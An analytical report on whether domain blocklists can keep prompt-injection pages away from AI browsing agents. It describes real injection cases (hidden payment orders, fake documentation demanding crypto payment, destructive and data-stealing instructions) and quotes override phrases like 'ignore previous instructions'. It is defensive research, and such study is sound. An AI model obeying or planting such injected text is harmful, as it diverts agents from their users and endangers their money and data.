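# Can domain reputation blocklists filter out prompt injection sources for browsing agents?

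## Browsing agents, prompt injection and blocklists

A browsing agent is an AI system that opens web pages and acts on them for a user. It can search, click, fill in forms and, if the user allows it, make payments. Perplexity's Comet browser and Google Chrome both include one, and developers can build their own with open-source frameworks such as Browser Use. These agents read pages written by strangers, which exposes them to indirect prompt injection, in which someone tries to divert an AI system from its user's task by placing instructions in content it reads.

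Browsers have long used blocklists against phishing and malware. A blocklist is a list of domains, hostnames or URLs that software refuses to load. An agent could check such a list before opening a page, so injections on listed pages would never reach it. How much this would help depends on where the injections are and which pages agents visit.

Suppose a user asks an agent to compare cordless vacuum cleaners, and the agent runs a search and opens a page of reviews. The page's code contains a sentence, hidden from human visitors, that tells any AI reader to send money to an account. Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, an April 2026 report from the security company Forcepoint, describes a similar live page. It had an HTML comment (a note in the page's source that browsers do not display) containing a PayPal link, an amount of $5,000 and step-by-step directions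 for confirming the payment. Sewani does not report that any agent paid.

### How a page becomes model input

A browsing agent runs in a loop that *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* (Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik, 2025) calls sense-plan-act. The agent observes the page, plans the next step, carries it out, and then observes the resulting page. A language model does the planning, and ordinary code around it, usually called the harness, does the rest.

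The harness can present a page to the model in two main ways. It can extract text from the DOM, the tree of elements a browser builds from a page's code, or it can take a screenshot and let a vision model pick out buttons and paragraphs. Some agents combine the two. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) explains that with text, the harness numbers each element and the model replies with an action and a number, such as a click on element 1582. With a screenshot, the model replies with coordinates.

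The harness combines the page with a description of the agent's role, the user's request, a record of earlier steps and a list of available tools, such as going to a URL, typing into a field or submitting a form. It sends all of this to the model as one input. Because the record carries over from step to step, a sentence from the review page may still be in the input when the agent reaches a checkout three pages later.

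Whether a hidden instruction reaches the model depends on how the harness extracts the page. An HTML comment doesn't appear in a screenshot, but the model receives it if the harness passes on the raw code. White text on a white background is also invisible in a screenshot, but text extraction picks it up. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested 100 different injections from live pages by asking 13 models to summarise the pages in four formats. The models followed the injected instruction in 3.9% of runs on plain text and 1.1% on HTML. The likely reason is that HTML keeps the markup showing that a passage was hidden, while plain text makes it look like part of the article. Some of the gap is an artefact, because the HTML versions were so long that a fifth of those runs ended in errors. Summarising is also a much simpler task than shopping,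 so these rates are weak evidence of how a full agent would behave.

Plain text also omits who supplied each part of the page. Browsers carefully keep content from different origins apart and limit what each can do to the others. Iqbal points out that once the harness has turned the page into text, an outside advertisement and the shop's own checkout button are both just words.

### Why a model may take page text for an instruction

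This confusion is preventable in older kinds of software. In SQL injection, an attacker types a database command into a form field and the database executes it. Developers prevent this by sending commands and data separately, so the database cannot treat a customer's name as a command, whatever characters it contains. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that language models offer no such separation. A model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and nothing in that process marks which text is data and which is instruction.

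Developers therefore try to train models to make this distinction. Early models learned to follow instructions but not to choose among them, according to *Understanding and Mitigating Role Spoofing in LLMs* (2026). Current agents learn an instruction hierarchy, in which the developer's system instructions outrank the user's, and the user's outrank anything in third-party content. *On Task, Off Track* (2026) offers a useful rule that page content may supply facts and even guidance for the task, but cannot on its own authorise a departure from it. In the vacuum cleaner example, the agent may properly change its recommendation because a page says one model's battery cannot be replaced, but it should not make a payment because a page orders one.

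Models learn to follow this hierarchy, but they can fail to. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) placed identical passages under different role labels (user, tool output and so on) and trained simple classifiers to recover the label from the model's internal activity. Because the wording never varied, the classifiers could learn only the label's effect on that activity. The team then ran them on text that was phrased like a user's request but labelled as tool output, and they mostly classified it as the user's. In 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, attacks succeeded about 2% of the time where this confusion was lowest and 70% where it was highest. On this account, the order to send money works when it sounds like something the user would write, and labelling it as web content has little effect.

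Training has made prompt injection harder but has not eliminated it. Iqbal, writing in October 2026, still treats the model as something an attacker can manipulate. This is a reason to add defenses outside the model, and a blocklist is about the simplest.

### Who can put text on a page

The injection surface is all the places from which injected text can reach an agent, including emails, shared documents and web pages. Four parties can add injected text to a web page, and the domain name reveals much more about some of them than others.

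The site's operator may be the attacker. Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* reports two such campaigns, which the security company Zscaler found. In one, a fake documentation page for a Python library contained instructions for coding agents to buy a $3 licence key by paying a cryptocurrency wallet. In the other, a site using a misspelt version of a well-known cryptocurrency tracker's address contained hidden instructions for agents to treat it as the authentic site. Blocklists are meant for sites like these, which have no honest use and can be blocked without harming anyone.

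An intruder, by contrast, breaks into somebody else's site and adds the text. If the vacuum cleaner page belongs to a shop that has traded honestly for ten years, its domain has an excellent record on the day of the attack. These injections are hard to identify in web crawls. Khodayari and colleagues sorted the injections they found into the operator's own content, contributions hosted by a platform (such as job advertisements) and user comments, and they would probably have classed an intruder's text as the operator's.

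Attacks can also come from a site's users. On a large shopping site, anyone with an account may be able to write a review or a listing. *BrowseSafe* (Zhang, Tenenholtz et al., 2025), a study of attacks on browser agents, gives the example of a malicious comment deep in a long forum thread that an agent has to summarise. An attacker doesn't need to hide such a comment in the page's code, since few people will read that far. The study also includes test pages on which a model rewrote visible passages to carry the attack in the page's own style.

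Finally, a third party such as an advertiser can supply text through a frame or script that the page loads. Iqbal cites measurements that found third parties on 92% of pages, and 66 third parties on the median site among the top thousand. The site's operator often does not know what these parties will show, and the page's address does not identify them. A browser may fetch an advertisement from a separate domain, which a filter could check. But a script can also write text directly into the main page, where the browser attributes it to the site.

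### Judging the source and judging the content

Blocklists began as a defence against spam in the late 1990s, when the internet engineers Dave Rand and Paul Vixie started keeping a list of IP addresses that had sent unwanted mail. Mail servers could check the list before accepting a message. Browser makers later applied the idea to malware and phishing, listing web addresses instead of mail senders. Most modern lists are based on domain reputation, an assessment of how risky a domain is that draws on its history, registration, hosting and past detections. Reputation is a matter of degree, but a blocklist reduces it to a decision to block or allow, which the software applies by checking the list just before loading a page.

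A domain blocklist filters pages by where they come from, while a content filter examines the words on the page. A content filter that searches for stock phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" is easy to evade because, as David C notes, an attacker can reword an order without limit. It also raises false alarms, since Sewani observes that the same phrases fill the articles in which security researchers explain the attack. Rewording doesn't get an attacker past a source filter once the domain is on the list. But the filter can only block or allow a whole domain, so if one review out of ten thousand on a shopping site contains an order to send money, it must either block the entire site or let the review through.

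Google uses both kinds in Chrome. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a classifier that checks every page the agent sees for injections, running alongside Safe Browsing, Google's existing service against dangerous sites. The design also restricts the agent to sites relevant to its task and requires the user's confirmation before it opens certain sensitive sites, such as banks. Both rules apply whether or not a site has a bad record. David C would put more emphasis on limiting what an agent can do once something has misled it than on keeping malicious text away from it. Blocklists do the latter. His ranking doesn't rule them out, but it does raise the question of how much malicious text they remove.

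Experience with phishing partly answers that question. A blocklist can block a listed page for an agent just as it does for a person, and it has the same basic limit, which is that somebody has to find a page before anybody can list it. People have to see a phishing page to be fooled by it, and some of them report it, but an injection can be a single sentence that no person ever sees, on a page that is otherwise exactly what it appears to be.

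### What share of harmful exposure would disappear?

If browsing agents never loaded blocklisted domains, they would avoid a fraction B / H of their harmful page visits. H is the number of page visits in a given period in which an agent reads text instructing it to act against its user's interests, and B is the number of those visits where the domain was already on the blocklist when the agent loaded the page.

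That fraction depends on several choices and assumptions. It covers only harmful injections, whereas Google's search of a public archive of web pages also found many pranks, attempts to promote a business in AI summaries, and requests that AI systems stay away. The ten domains listed in Sewani's report include one with the $5,000 payment order and one whose hidden text asks for a poem about corn. Blocking both would remove two injections, but only one that threatens the user's money. The domain must already be listed when the agent visits, because a later listing protects only later visitors. The fraction also assumes that an agent turned away from one page does not go on to another poisoned one. Finally, it measures exposure, and the share of successful attacks removed would be the same only if the attack success rate, the share of injection attempts that make the agent do what the attacker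 wants, were equal on listed and unlisted pages.

H counts visits, whereas most published figures count pages or domains. The results can differ enormously. Imagine 1,000 attacker-run sites, each with one malicious page that agents open once, and one large marketplace with 50 poisoned listings that agents open 200 times each. A blocklist contains 900 of the attackers' sites and, naturally, not the marketplace. The numbers are invented, but the arithmetic is not:

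| Unit counted | On attackers' own sites | On the marketplace | Blocked | Share removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Domains | 1,000 | 1 | 900 | 90% |
| Pages | 1,000 | 50 | 900 | 86% |
| Agent visits | 1,000 | 10,000 | 900 | 8% |

Counting domains can also understate how much exposure a blocklist removes. If one fake documentation page reached the top of the search results, agents might open it thousands of times, but blocking it would add only one domain to the count.

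The number of pages containing an injection is a poor guide to the number of domains hosting it. Khodayari and colleagues found one stock injection on 1,463 pages at only two hosts (a host is a named server, such as shop.example.com) and another on 1,019 pages at 1,018 hosts. Blocking the first would take two blocklist entries, but blocking the second would take about a thousand. The term "domain" is also ambiguous, because a service that lends subdomains to thousands of publishers has thousands of hostnames but only one registrable domain (the part of an address that someone registers, such as example.com).

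The closest evidence on visits is *The Adoption and Usage of AI Agents* (2025), a study of Comet between July and October 2025. It recorded which website the agent worked on for each request. Google Docs, email services, LinkedIn, YouTube and Amazon together accounted for 43% of all requests, and Amazon alone accounted for 43% of requests related to shopping for goods. B / H cannot be calculated from these figures because the users were early adopters and the study counted requests rather than page loads and did not measure harm. But the figures suggest that an agent helping the user who wants a vacuum cleaner may well compare products on Amazon. Outsiders write the reviews there, and no blocklist could include Amazon without making the agent useless for shopping.

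## How a reputation filter works inside a browsing agent

The agent comparing vacuum cleaners has a page of search results open, and its model picks a link. Before the browser loads the page behind that link, software has to check whether the address is on a blocklist. Google publishes the whole procedure for Safe Browsing, which makes it a convenient example. Suppose the link leads to this invented address:

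`reviews.example.com/vacuums/cordless.html?page=2`

### Looking up one address

The software first normalises the address, because the same address can be written in many ways. Following the rules in Google's *URLs and Hashing*, it puts the hostname in lower case, decodes percent-encoded characters, tidies up stray dots and slashes, and removes the fragment (anything after a # sign, which usually marks a place within the page). Without this step, an address with a few capital letters in its hostname would not match its blocklist entry.

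Because normalisation removes the fragment, no Safe Browsing entry can block a link with malicious instructions after the # without also blocking the honest page it points to. Browsers don't send the fragment to the site, so the page usually loads normally whatever the fragment contains. An attacker could therefore put instructions in a link to a reputable site, and the model would read them if the harness includes the current address in its input. *Piloting Claude for Chrome*, Anthropic's August 2025 post about its browser extension, mentions URL text as one place an injection can hide.

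Next, the software builds a set of strings from the address. It combines the hostname and its parent domain each with the full path, the path without the query (the part after the question mark), and every folder above the page. In the example, two hostnames and four paths give eight strings, from the complete address down to `example.com/`. Longer addresses can produce up to 30. The address counts as listed if any of its strings is on the list.

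The list contains hashes. The software runs each string through SHA-256, a function that turns any text into a 32-byte value, and keeps the first four bytes, called the prefix. It then looks for that prefix in a local copy of the list, which also holds only prefixes. Four bytes allow only about 4.3 billion values, so a harmless string will sometimes match by accident. *Catch Me (On Time) If You Can* (Bell, Paterson and Cavallaro, 2019) reports that Safe Browsing listed about 1.07 million dangerous sites in one week of September 2017. If each site had one entry, a harmless string would match about once in 4,000 tries, and an address with eight strings about once in 500. When a prefix matches, the software therefore sends it to Google's server, which returns the full hashes that begin with it. The software blocks the page only if one of them is identical to the string's full hash. Google receives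 only the prefix, which protects the user's privacy.

Google's *Local List Mode* describes a procedure in which the software contacts the server only after an address matches the local list, so a page that Google has listed since the last download isn't blocked. In Google's *Real Time Mode*, the software asks the server about every address unless one of its strings is in a downloaded cache of sites that are probably harmless. For those sites, it relies on the local list. Big shopping sites are presumably in the cache, so a new entry for one poisoned product page would take effect only when the local list next updates.

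If the server doesn't respond, the local procedure treats the address as safe. That is reasonable for people, who would otherwise lose access to harmless pages whenever the service failed. A developer could instead have an agent treat the address as unsafe, since the agent can wait and try again.

The address the model chooses may also redirect to another. Bell and colleagues checked every address in each chain of redirects they found on Twitter, because a blocklisted address can be hidden partway along the chain. In one month they found 376 blocklisted short links from Bitly, and those links had received 991,012 clicks. A browser can check each redirect as it follows it, but a harness that checks only the address the model chose will miss the destination of a short link.

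The browser then requests the page's frames, scripts and images, each with its own address, and the filter can check those addresses too. If a listed domain supplies an advertisement in a frame, the browser can leave the frame empty and still load the reviews. The reviews usually come from the site's own servers, so the filter allows or blocks them along with the page.

### What an entry can name

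Because the software tries several strings, a list entry can be as broad as a whole domain or as narrow as one page.

| Entry | What it misses | What it wrongly blocks if one review is malicious |
|---|---|---|
| Registrable domain: `example.com` | The attacker's other domains | The entire site, including its shop and help pages |
| Hostname: `reviews.example.com` | The same review on `shop.example.com` | Every other review |
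| Path: `reviews.example.com/vacuums/` | The same review in a folder called `/sale/` | Every other vacuum cleaner review |
| Full URL: `reviews.example.com/vacuums/cordless.html?page=2` | The same review on page 3 | The other reviews on page 2 |

If the attacker owns `example.com`, the broadest blocklist entry is clearly the best. The attacker can create new hostnames and paths at almost no cost, so narrower entries soon go out of date, but replacing the domain means paying for another one.

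If the attacker has only posted a product review, the only blocklist entry most users would tolerate is the page's full URL, which doesn't work very well. Newer reviews will push the malicious one onto a later page with a different URL, and it may also appear on the reviewer's profile and in the site's search results. An entry without the query string would cover every page number, but it would also block all the reviews of that product.

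Full-URL entries are more useful against phishing than against prompt injection. A phishing email sends its victims to a particular address, so listing that address blocks the link in every copy of the email. An attacker doesn't need to send anyone a link to an injection, because agents can reach it through the site's ordinary menus and search pages, at whatever address the site uses.

### Scores for domains that nobody has listed

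Security companies can estimate the risk of an unlisted domain from facts about it, typically with a statistical model trained on domains that turned out to be harmful or harmless.

A recently registered domain looks riskier because many attackers use a domain soon after buying it and drop it once it appears on blocklists. Registration records can show that someone bought fifty similar names on the same day. Hosting records show which other domains share the same servers, and a domain looks worse if those domains have been found distributing malware. Links from established sites count in a domain's favour, although attackers can buy or plant them. Past detections on the domain count against it, sometimes long after the owner has cleaned it up.

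Even together, these facts don't prove that a domain is malicious. As an invented example, suppose that one in 500 of the unfamiliar domains an agent visits is malicious. Suppose also that malicious domains are 20 times as likely as harmless ones to be less than a week old, and 10 times as likely to share a server with a known attack site. For a domain with both features, the odds of being malicious are 1/499 × 20 × 10, or about 0.4. That is a 29% chance, so blocking every such domain would be a mistake about seven times out of ten. The calculation also treats the two features as independent, but harmless new sites often start on cheap shared servers too, so the second feature is weaker evidence than it appears. A company might therefore use a score to trigger a warning or a closer inspection, and reserve outright blocking for confirmed attacks.

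This kind of scoring should also work against attackers who register domains to trap agents, like the one who built the fake documentation page for a Python library, since they buy domains and servers much as phishers do. It won't help with an injected sentence hidden on a legitimate site that has a good record.

### Block pages that an agent cannot pass

When a browser finds a match, it normally shows a full-page warning, often with a small link for people who want to continue anyway. Most people turn back, but a browsing agent may treat the warning as an ordinary page with a link to click.

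*Privacy Practices of Browser Agents* (Ukani, Haddadi and colleagues, 2025) tested a related warning by sending agents to a shoe shop whose security certificate no recognised authority had issued. The browser warned about the certificate, but Browser Use, running a Claude Sonnet model, clicked through to finish its task. *CredLeakBench* (2026), which tests whether agents give away passwords on suspicious sites, found large differences between models and between types of cue. Claude Opus 4.8 leaked credentials in 4.7% of cases with a certificate warning and 51.6% with an unencrypted connection. Two small open models, Qwen3.5-9B and Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, often leaked them despite the certificate warning. The protection from a warning that the model can dismiss therefore depends on the model's judgement, which injected text may already have influenced.

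Microsoft Edge uses SmartScreen, the company's counterpart to Google Safe Browsing. Microsoft's *Considerations for Safe Agentic Browsing* (2025), published with the first preview of Edge's agent mode, explains that SmartScreen blocks suspicious sites while the Copilot assistant controls the browser, and that the agent cannot bypass the block page. Once Microsoft confirms that a site is a scam or distributes malware, SmartScreen can block it for all Edge users within minutes.

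Microsoft described a separate global blocklist of sites that are unsafe for Copilot to read, which it can update within hours. This list is much closer to a blocklist for prompt injection, since a page can be harmless to a person and still unsafe for an agent. But Microsoft did not give the list's size, the criteria for adding a site, or the number of visits the list blocks.

### Blocking topics and blocking attacks

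These products also block sites for reasons that have little to do with detected attacks. Microsoft's *Browse with Copilot*, the current help page for the same feature, lists adult content and gambling as examples of what Edge's blocklists keep the agent from visiting. Users can block additional sites, and in the recommended setting the agent also needs approval for sites outside a curated list. According to Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely*, the extension cannot open adult sites or known sources of pirated content, and it asks for permission before opening financial sites. In the 2025 pilot, Anthropic blocked financial sites altogether.

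Blocking financial sites protects the user's money but removes little harmful text, so it adds almost nothing to B, the number of harmful visits blocked. A bank's own website is unlikely to contain an injection, but it is where an agent that has already been hijacked could do the most damage. Blocking piracy sites may add more to B if those sites carry more malicious advertising than most, but Anthropic gives no figures.

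Topic blocks don't require anyone to discover an attack first, so a gambling site can be on the list before anyone puts an injection on it. But they don't help with the vacuum cleaner reviews, because no sensible list of risky topics would include household appliances.

### How many known phishing pages AI browsers block

In 2025, the browser security company LayerX tested AI browsers against phishing pages. It took the 100 most recent attacks from public reporting services such as OpenPhish and PhishTank and opened each one in five browsers. LayerX found that the AI browsers Comet and Genspark each blocked only 7%. eSecurity Planet's *LayerX Exposes Critical Flaw in OpenAI’s ChatGPT Atlas Browser* reports that Atlas blocked 5.8% of 103 attacks in a later LayerX test. LayerX sells a browser add-on that it says blocks 98%, so it has an interest in other products scoring low.

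Its figures for ordinary browsers are at least plausible when compared with a testing lab's. AV-Comparatives' *Anti-Phishing Comparative Test* (2025), which several vendors supported, used 250 phishing pages in November 2025.

| Browser | Blocked, LayerX | Blocked, AV-Comparatives |
|---|---|---|
| Firefox | not tested | 74% |
| Edge | 54% | 65% |
| Chrome | 47% | 41% |
| Dia (AI browser) | 46% | not tested |
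| Comet (AI browser) | 7% | not tested |
| Genspark (AI browser) | 7% | not tested |
| Atlas (AI browser, later test) | 5.8% | not tested |

None of the browsers in the lab's test blocked any of 250 harmless pages. Chrome's block rate fell from 70% to 41% over the lab's four tests in 2025, while Opera's rose from 45% to 74%. Chrome and Firefox both used Safe Browsing when Bell and colleagues wrote in 2019, so the gap between them in the table probably isn't due only to the choice of list.

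Dia's results matched Chrome's on 97% of pages, which suggests that Dia uses Google's list. LayerX found no sign that Comet or Genspark blocked any pages based on reputation. The few pages they stopped had faulty security certificates, so they apparently didn't use Google's list.

Ukani and colleagues, some of whom work for the browser maker Brave, reached a similar result by a simpler method. They asked eight agents to open and summarise a harmless test page that Google keeps on the Safe Browsing list. Six, including Comet, showed no warning. For the other two, Claude for Chrome and Claude Computer Use, the warning came from the browsers they were controlling. The team tested only one page, and they told the developers about the problems at least 90 days before publication, so some of these products may have changed since.

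Three of the six agents, ChatGPT Agent, Google's Project Mariner and Browserbase's Director, run their browser on a company's servers. The user's browser never requests the page, so its Safe Browsing check never runs. The remote browser could do its own check, but none of the three showed a warning. The other three, Comet, Browser Use and Amazon's Nova Act, run locally and didn't show one either. Some agent tools download a page's text without using a browser, so no lookup happens unless the developer adds one. LayerX notes that Google sells access to its lists through a service called Web Risk, which developers could use for this.

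Guardio's *Scamlexity* is not evidence of the same fault, because its test used a new site that was unlikely to be on any blocklist. Guardio, another security vendor, built a fake Walmart shop with an AI tool and told Comet to buy an Apple Watch there. The page loaded although, by Guardio's account, Safe Browsing was active, but even a perfect lookup would probably have let it through.

All of these tests used phishing pages or a stand-in for one. An agent that never checks a blocklist will open a listed injection page just as readily, so the missing lookup is also a problem for prompt injection. The percentages apply only to phishing, because they depend on how quickly people and scanners find phishing pages.

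### Why Anthropic's pilot figures do not measure blocking

Anthropic's pilot is one of the few cases where a company added site blocks and published attack success rates before and after. Its testers tried 123 attacks based on 29 scenarios while the agent worked without asking for confirmation. The attacks succeeded 23.6% of the time without the new defences and 11.2% of the time with them.

Those defences included site blocks, but Anthropic had also rewritten the model's standing instructions and begun testing classifiers that look for suspicious text and unusual requests for data. It did not publish a separate result for each change, so outsiders cannot tell how much the blocks contributed. The one successful attack that the post describes in detail was an email telling the agent to delete the user's messages. The agent read it in the user's own inbox, so blocking adult or financial sites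 would not have stopped it.

Anthropic published a chart with its Claude Opus 4.5 model showing how often attacks succeeded when an automated attacker had 100 attempts in each test environment. The rate was 8.0% for the model alone, 7.6% with the extension's original safeguards and 1.4% with improved ones. For the three other models in the chart, the original safeguards lowered the rate by between 0.9 and 3.1 percentage points. If those safeguards included the pilot's site blocks, as seems likely, the blocks had little effect on this test. They could still be useful on the open web, because the test pages may not have belonged to any blocked category. Anthropic attributes its progress to training, better classifiers and human testers, and does not mention site blocking.

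The company's current help page gives an attack success rate below 0.08% for Claude Opus 4.8 in internal tests that combine techniques known to work. This rate isn't directly comparable with the earlier 11.2%, because the attacks, the model and the safeguards have all changed. Still, a lower success rate leaves fewer successful attacks for a blocklist to prevent. If an agent faced 10,000 attacks, a list that blocked half of them at random would prevent 560 successful attacks at an 11.2% success rate and four at 0.08%.

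## Where injected instructions have been found on the web

A blocklist can stop only injections on domains that somebody is willing to block, even if every agent checks the list before loading a page. In 2026 several teams searched the web for injections and found far more pranks and protests than attacks, and most were on obscure sites. But the searches missed many of the places where agents do much of their work.

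### A search of 1.2 billion URLs

Khodayari and colleagues ran the largest search with published totals. They processed 1.2 billion URLs on 24.8 million hosts, about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages collected by an automated crawler.

The researchers searched for fixed phrases because they judged machine-learning detectors too expensive to run on so many pages. They collected known wordings from research papers, company reports and blog posts, then swapped in alternatives such as "commands" for "instructions", which gave them 3,963 phrases. These matched 27,860 passages on 999 hosts. Two reviewers then separated real instructions to AI systems from articles and tutorials about them, often labelling near-identical matches as a group. This left 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages across 285 hosts.

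That is about eight pages per million. An agent that opened 100 archived pages a day at random would come across an injection roughly every three and a half years. Real agents don't choose pages at random, and the search missed any injection with unfamiliar wording, so the figure is a minimum.

The team also searched Censys and Shodan, which scan the internet by IP address and so find servers that no page links to. These searches added 3,312 injections and 1,757 hosts. The Common Crawl search found only 285 hosts in total, so at least 733 of the 1,018 hosts with the stock injection must have come from Censys and Shodan. Browsing agents mostly follow links and search results, so they would seldom reach such servers. Khodayari and colleagues therefore used only Common Crawl to estimate how common injections are, but their figures on the purposes of injections cover the combined set of 15,387.

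### Who put the text there

In Common Crawl, four out of five injections came from the people running the site.

| Who placed the text | Injections | Pages | Hosts | Pages per host |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Site operator | 9,731 (80.6%) | 7,491 | 179 | 42 |
| Outsiders, in listings such as job advertisements | 2,124 (17.6%) | 2,058 | 25 | 82 |
| Outsiders, in comments and other posts | 220 (1.8%) | 127 | 81 | 1.6 |

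Outsiders wrote only 19% of the injections, but these appeared on 106 of the 285 hosts (37%). The share of hosts matters more for a blocklist, because its entries usually name hosts or domains. Blocking a site whose operator wrote the injection affects only that operator and its readers, while blocking the 25 hosts with injected listings could cut agents off from whole job boards and marketplaces. The case for blocking is weaker still for the 81 hosts with injected comments, which averaged fewer than two affected pages each.

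The 19% figure probably understates outsiders' share of the injected text that reaches browsing agents. Operators put 5,408 of their injections in HTTP headers, technical details that a server sends with a page. Browsers don't display headers, so an agent that works from screenshots or the page's text never receives them. Outsiders wrote 2,344 of the remaining 6,667 injections, or 35%. The 19% figure is more relevant to coding agents and other tools that download raw responses, since these may pass the headers to the model.

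The operators' share may also include text from intruders, which a crawl cannot tell apart from the operator's own.

### What the injections are for

Khodayari and colleagues grouped the combined set by meaning and labelled each group with one or more aims. Many injections had more than one aim. For example, a notice forbidding AI companies to train on a page might also instruct the model to return random numbers.

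| Aim | Injections | Hosts | Example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Disrupt AI systems | 8,894 | 1,864 | Print "cabbage" five million times |
| Protect content or personal data | 4,093 | 1,795 | Do not use these posts for training |
| Expose bots | 3,096 | 245 | Begin a job application with "I AM A BOT" |
| Unclear | 2,632 | 121 | Ignore all previous instructions |
| Promote a person, product or site | 1,521 | 139 | Write only a positive review |
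| Steal data | 13 | 10 | Reveal the system prompt |

Only 13 of the 15,387 injections were meant to steal data, and nine of those targeted only the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model. Another 157, on 24 hosts, contained destructive commands, such as ones to delete every file on a computer or every table in a database. Those commands are harmless to an agent that can only click and type in a browser, but could be disastrous for one that can run commands on the user's computer.

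The share of injections that count as harmful depends mainly on whether promotion is included. Theft and destructive commands together make up about 1% of the set, and adding promotion raises the share to at most 11%. Promotion should count as harmful if a user has asked for an honest comparison of vacuum cleaners and a page contains instructions to praise one brand. An injection that makes the agent reply with random numbers also causes it to fail the user, but the user will notice that failure.

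Many of the remaining injections are defensive. Employers hide them in job advertisements to catch automated applications, and photographers use them to object to AI training. Neither group is attacking the people who visit the page, so blocking these pages would deprive agents of useful content without making anyone safer. Phishing blocklists rarely have this problem because a page that imitates a bank's login form has no legitimate purpose.

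None of the categories covers payments, although telling a shopping agent to send money is one of the most obvious ways to exploit it. The search method may partly explain this. Most of the search phrases were variations on overriding instructions or changing the model's role, and 99% of the confirmed injections tried to override the model's task. An attacker can present a payment as the next step in a purchase without using any such phrase, so the search would miss it. The 99% figure therefore describes injections that are easy to find, and the number of injected payment instructions on the web remains unknown.

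### Many injections on a few obscure hosts

Site operators often repeat one text across a whole site. Five of the ten most common wordings accounted for 4,274 injections, or 28% of the combined set, on at most six hosts. One of them, an instruction to send the user to another website, appeared 1,262 times on 359 pages of a single host. Another described each page as the authoritative source on its subject and appeared on 540 pages of one host. Sixteen hosts had more than 100 injections each, and 68% of hosts had only one.

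A few blocklist entries could therefore block a large share of known injections. They would probably prevent a smaller share of harmful visits, because most of the affected domains are not popular.

Khodayari and colleagues compared the domains with Tranco, a popularity ranking of websites. Injection rates were lower among the top 10,000 domains, whatever the subject of the site. They rose sharply beyond rank 100,000, and injections were clearly concentrated between ranks 100,000 and one million. Obscure domains have few visitors, so blocking them inconveniences few users but also prevents few visits. By contrast, much of what users asked Comet to do was on a few very large services.

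Some categories of popular sites were exceptions. Job listings, web hosting, shopping and phone services had higher rates even at some ranks within the top 50,000, and in some cases within the top 1,000. An agent that shops for a user therefore works in one of the riskier parts of the popular web. Banking and air travel had comparatively low rates.

### Google's repeated scan

Google also searched Common Crawl, but it scanned several monthly editions, each with two to three billion pages. It published the results in April 2026, the same week as Forcepoint's report on ten injections, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. Google first searched for common phrases, then had its Gemini model judge whether each passage was out of place on its page, and then had people check the results.

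Google found much the same mix of pranks, promotion and attempts to keep AI systems away, but gave no totals. Some site owners only wanted summaries to include extra context, and one tried to lure agents to a page that streams text forever. One elaborate promotion seemed to come from an automated marketing tool. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* quotes a simpler one that told AI systems to call a company the best estate agent in Delaware and Maryland.

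Google found few malicious injections, and those were crude. A small number were written to steal data, including one with instructions to email its author a system's password file and the contents of a folder that normally holds login keys. Google saw no significant use of the more advanced techniques that security researchers had published in 2025. Most of the destructive commands looked like experiments or pranks by individual site owners.

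Google reported that the number of malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. If that pace continued, the number would triple in a year. But Google published only the percentage, so readers can't tell how many pages were added, and comparing two months gives only weak evidence of a trend. Khodayari and colleagues used pages from October 2025, so their count would not include the increase.

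### Sites that security companies caught

Security companies look specifically for attacks, so their examples are more malicious. *Fooling AI Agents*, published in March 2026 by Palo Alto Networks' research team, Unit 42, uses the company's data on web pages. Of the aims it recorded, 28.6% were to produce irrelevant output, 14.2% to destroy data, and 9.5% to get past AI content moderation. Destructive commands made up only 1% of Khodayari and colleagues' combined set. Unit 42 doesn't say how many pages its percentages cover, so they can't show how common attacks are.

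One page advertised military-style glasses at a fake discount, with invented customer comments. Its code contained 24 attempts to persuade an AI ad reviewer to approve it. The page's creators had labelled each layer of hiding methods in the code. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case of such an attack fooling an ad reviewer in real use.

Unit 42 published the addresses of 16 sites. From its descriptions, they can be sorted roughly as follows:

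| Type of domain | Sites | What the text was for |
|---|---|---|
| Own domain, apparently built for a scam | 3 | Recommend a fake betting site; approve an advertisement; buy running shoes |
| Own domain, payment order, other purpose unclear | 2 | Send $5,000 through PayPal |
| Own domain, business or content library | 2 | Praise a spa; make a donation |
| Own domain, personal site | 3 | Disclose a company's contacts; endorse a job candidate; print "cabbage" |
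| Own domain, owner unclear | 3 | Delete a database; produce nonsense; one not described |
| Subdomain of a hosting or shop service | 3 | Delete files; buy a subscription; one checkout page for the glasses |

Thirteen of the 16 sites have their own domains, so they could be added to a blocklist without blocking unrelated sites. But only the five sites in the first two rows seem to have nothing that users would miss. Blocking a personal site because of a joke about cabbage would also block its owner's writing on other subjects. The other three sites are subdomains of services with many other customers, so their blocklist entries should cover only the subdomain.

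None of the 16 addresses that Unit 42 published belongs to a large platform, but large platforms may still contain injections. Unit 42 published the addresses as indicators of compromise, which defenders use to block or search for threats. Listing a marketplace because of one poisoned review would be of little use to them, however many agents read the review.

The two campaigns that Zscaler found are better targets for a blocklist. Infosecurity Magazine reported them in July 2026. The fake Python documentation was one of ten similar sites, which covered subjects such as restaurant bookings, visa applications and image licensing. Each site had a matching GitHub repository that linked to it. The attacker had also filled the documentation page with search terms so that agents looking for help with the package would find it.

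The payment order on that page didn't need to override anything. Part of it was in structured data, which is code that describes a page to search engines. That code presented a $3 licence as the fix for an error message and included a payment link. Similar text was positioned off the screen. A developer who opened the site in an ordinary browser saw the same demand for payment, so the scam also targeted people.

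Four of the 26 models Zscaler tested made the payment the page requested. The attacker's cryptocurrency wallet had received money, but in larger amounts than the page requested, so those payments may have come from earlier scams. Zscaler didn't identify any real agent that had paid.

The other campaign, which imitated a cryptocurrency tracker, also had its own domain, bringing the total to 11. These domains resemble phishing sites closely enough that the same blocking methods work fairly well on them. A blocklist would not include GitHub itself, but it would stop an agent from opening the sites that the repositories link to.

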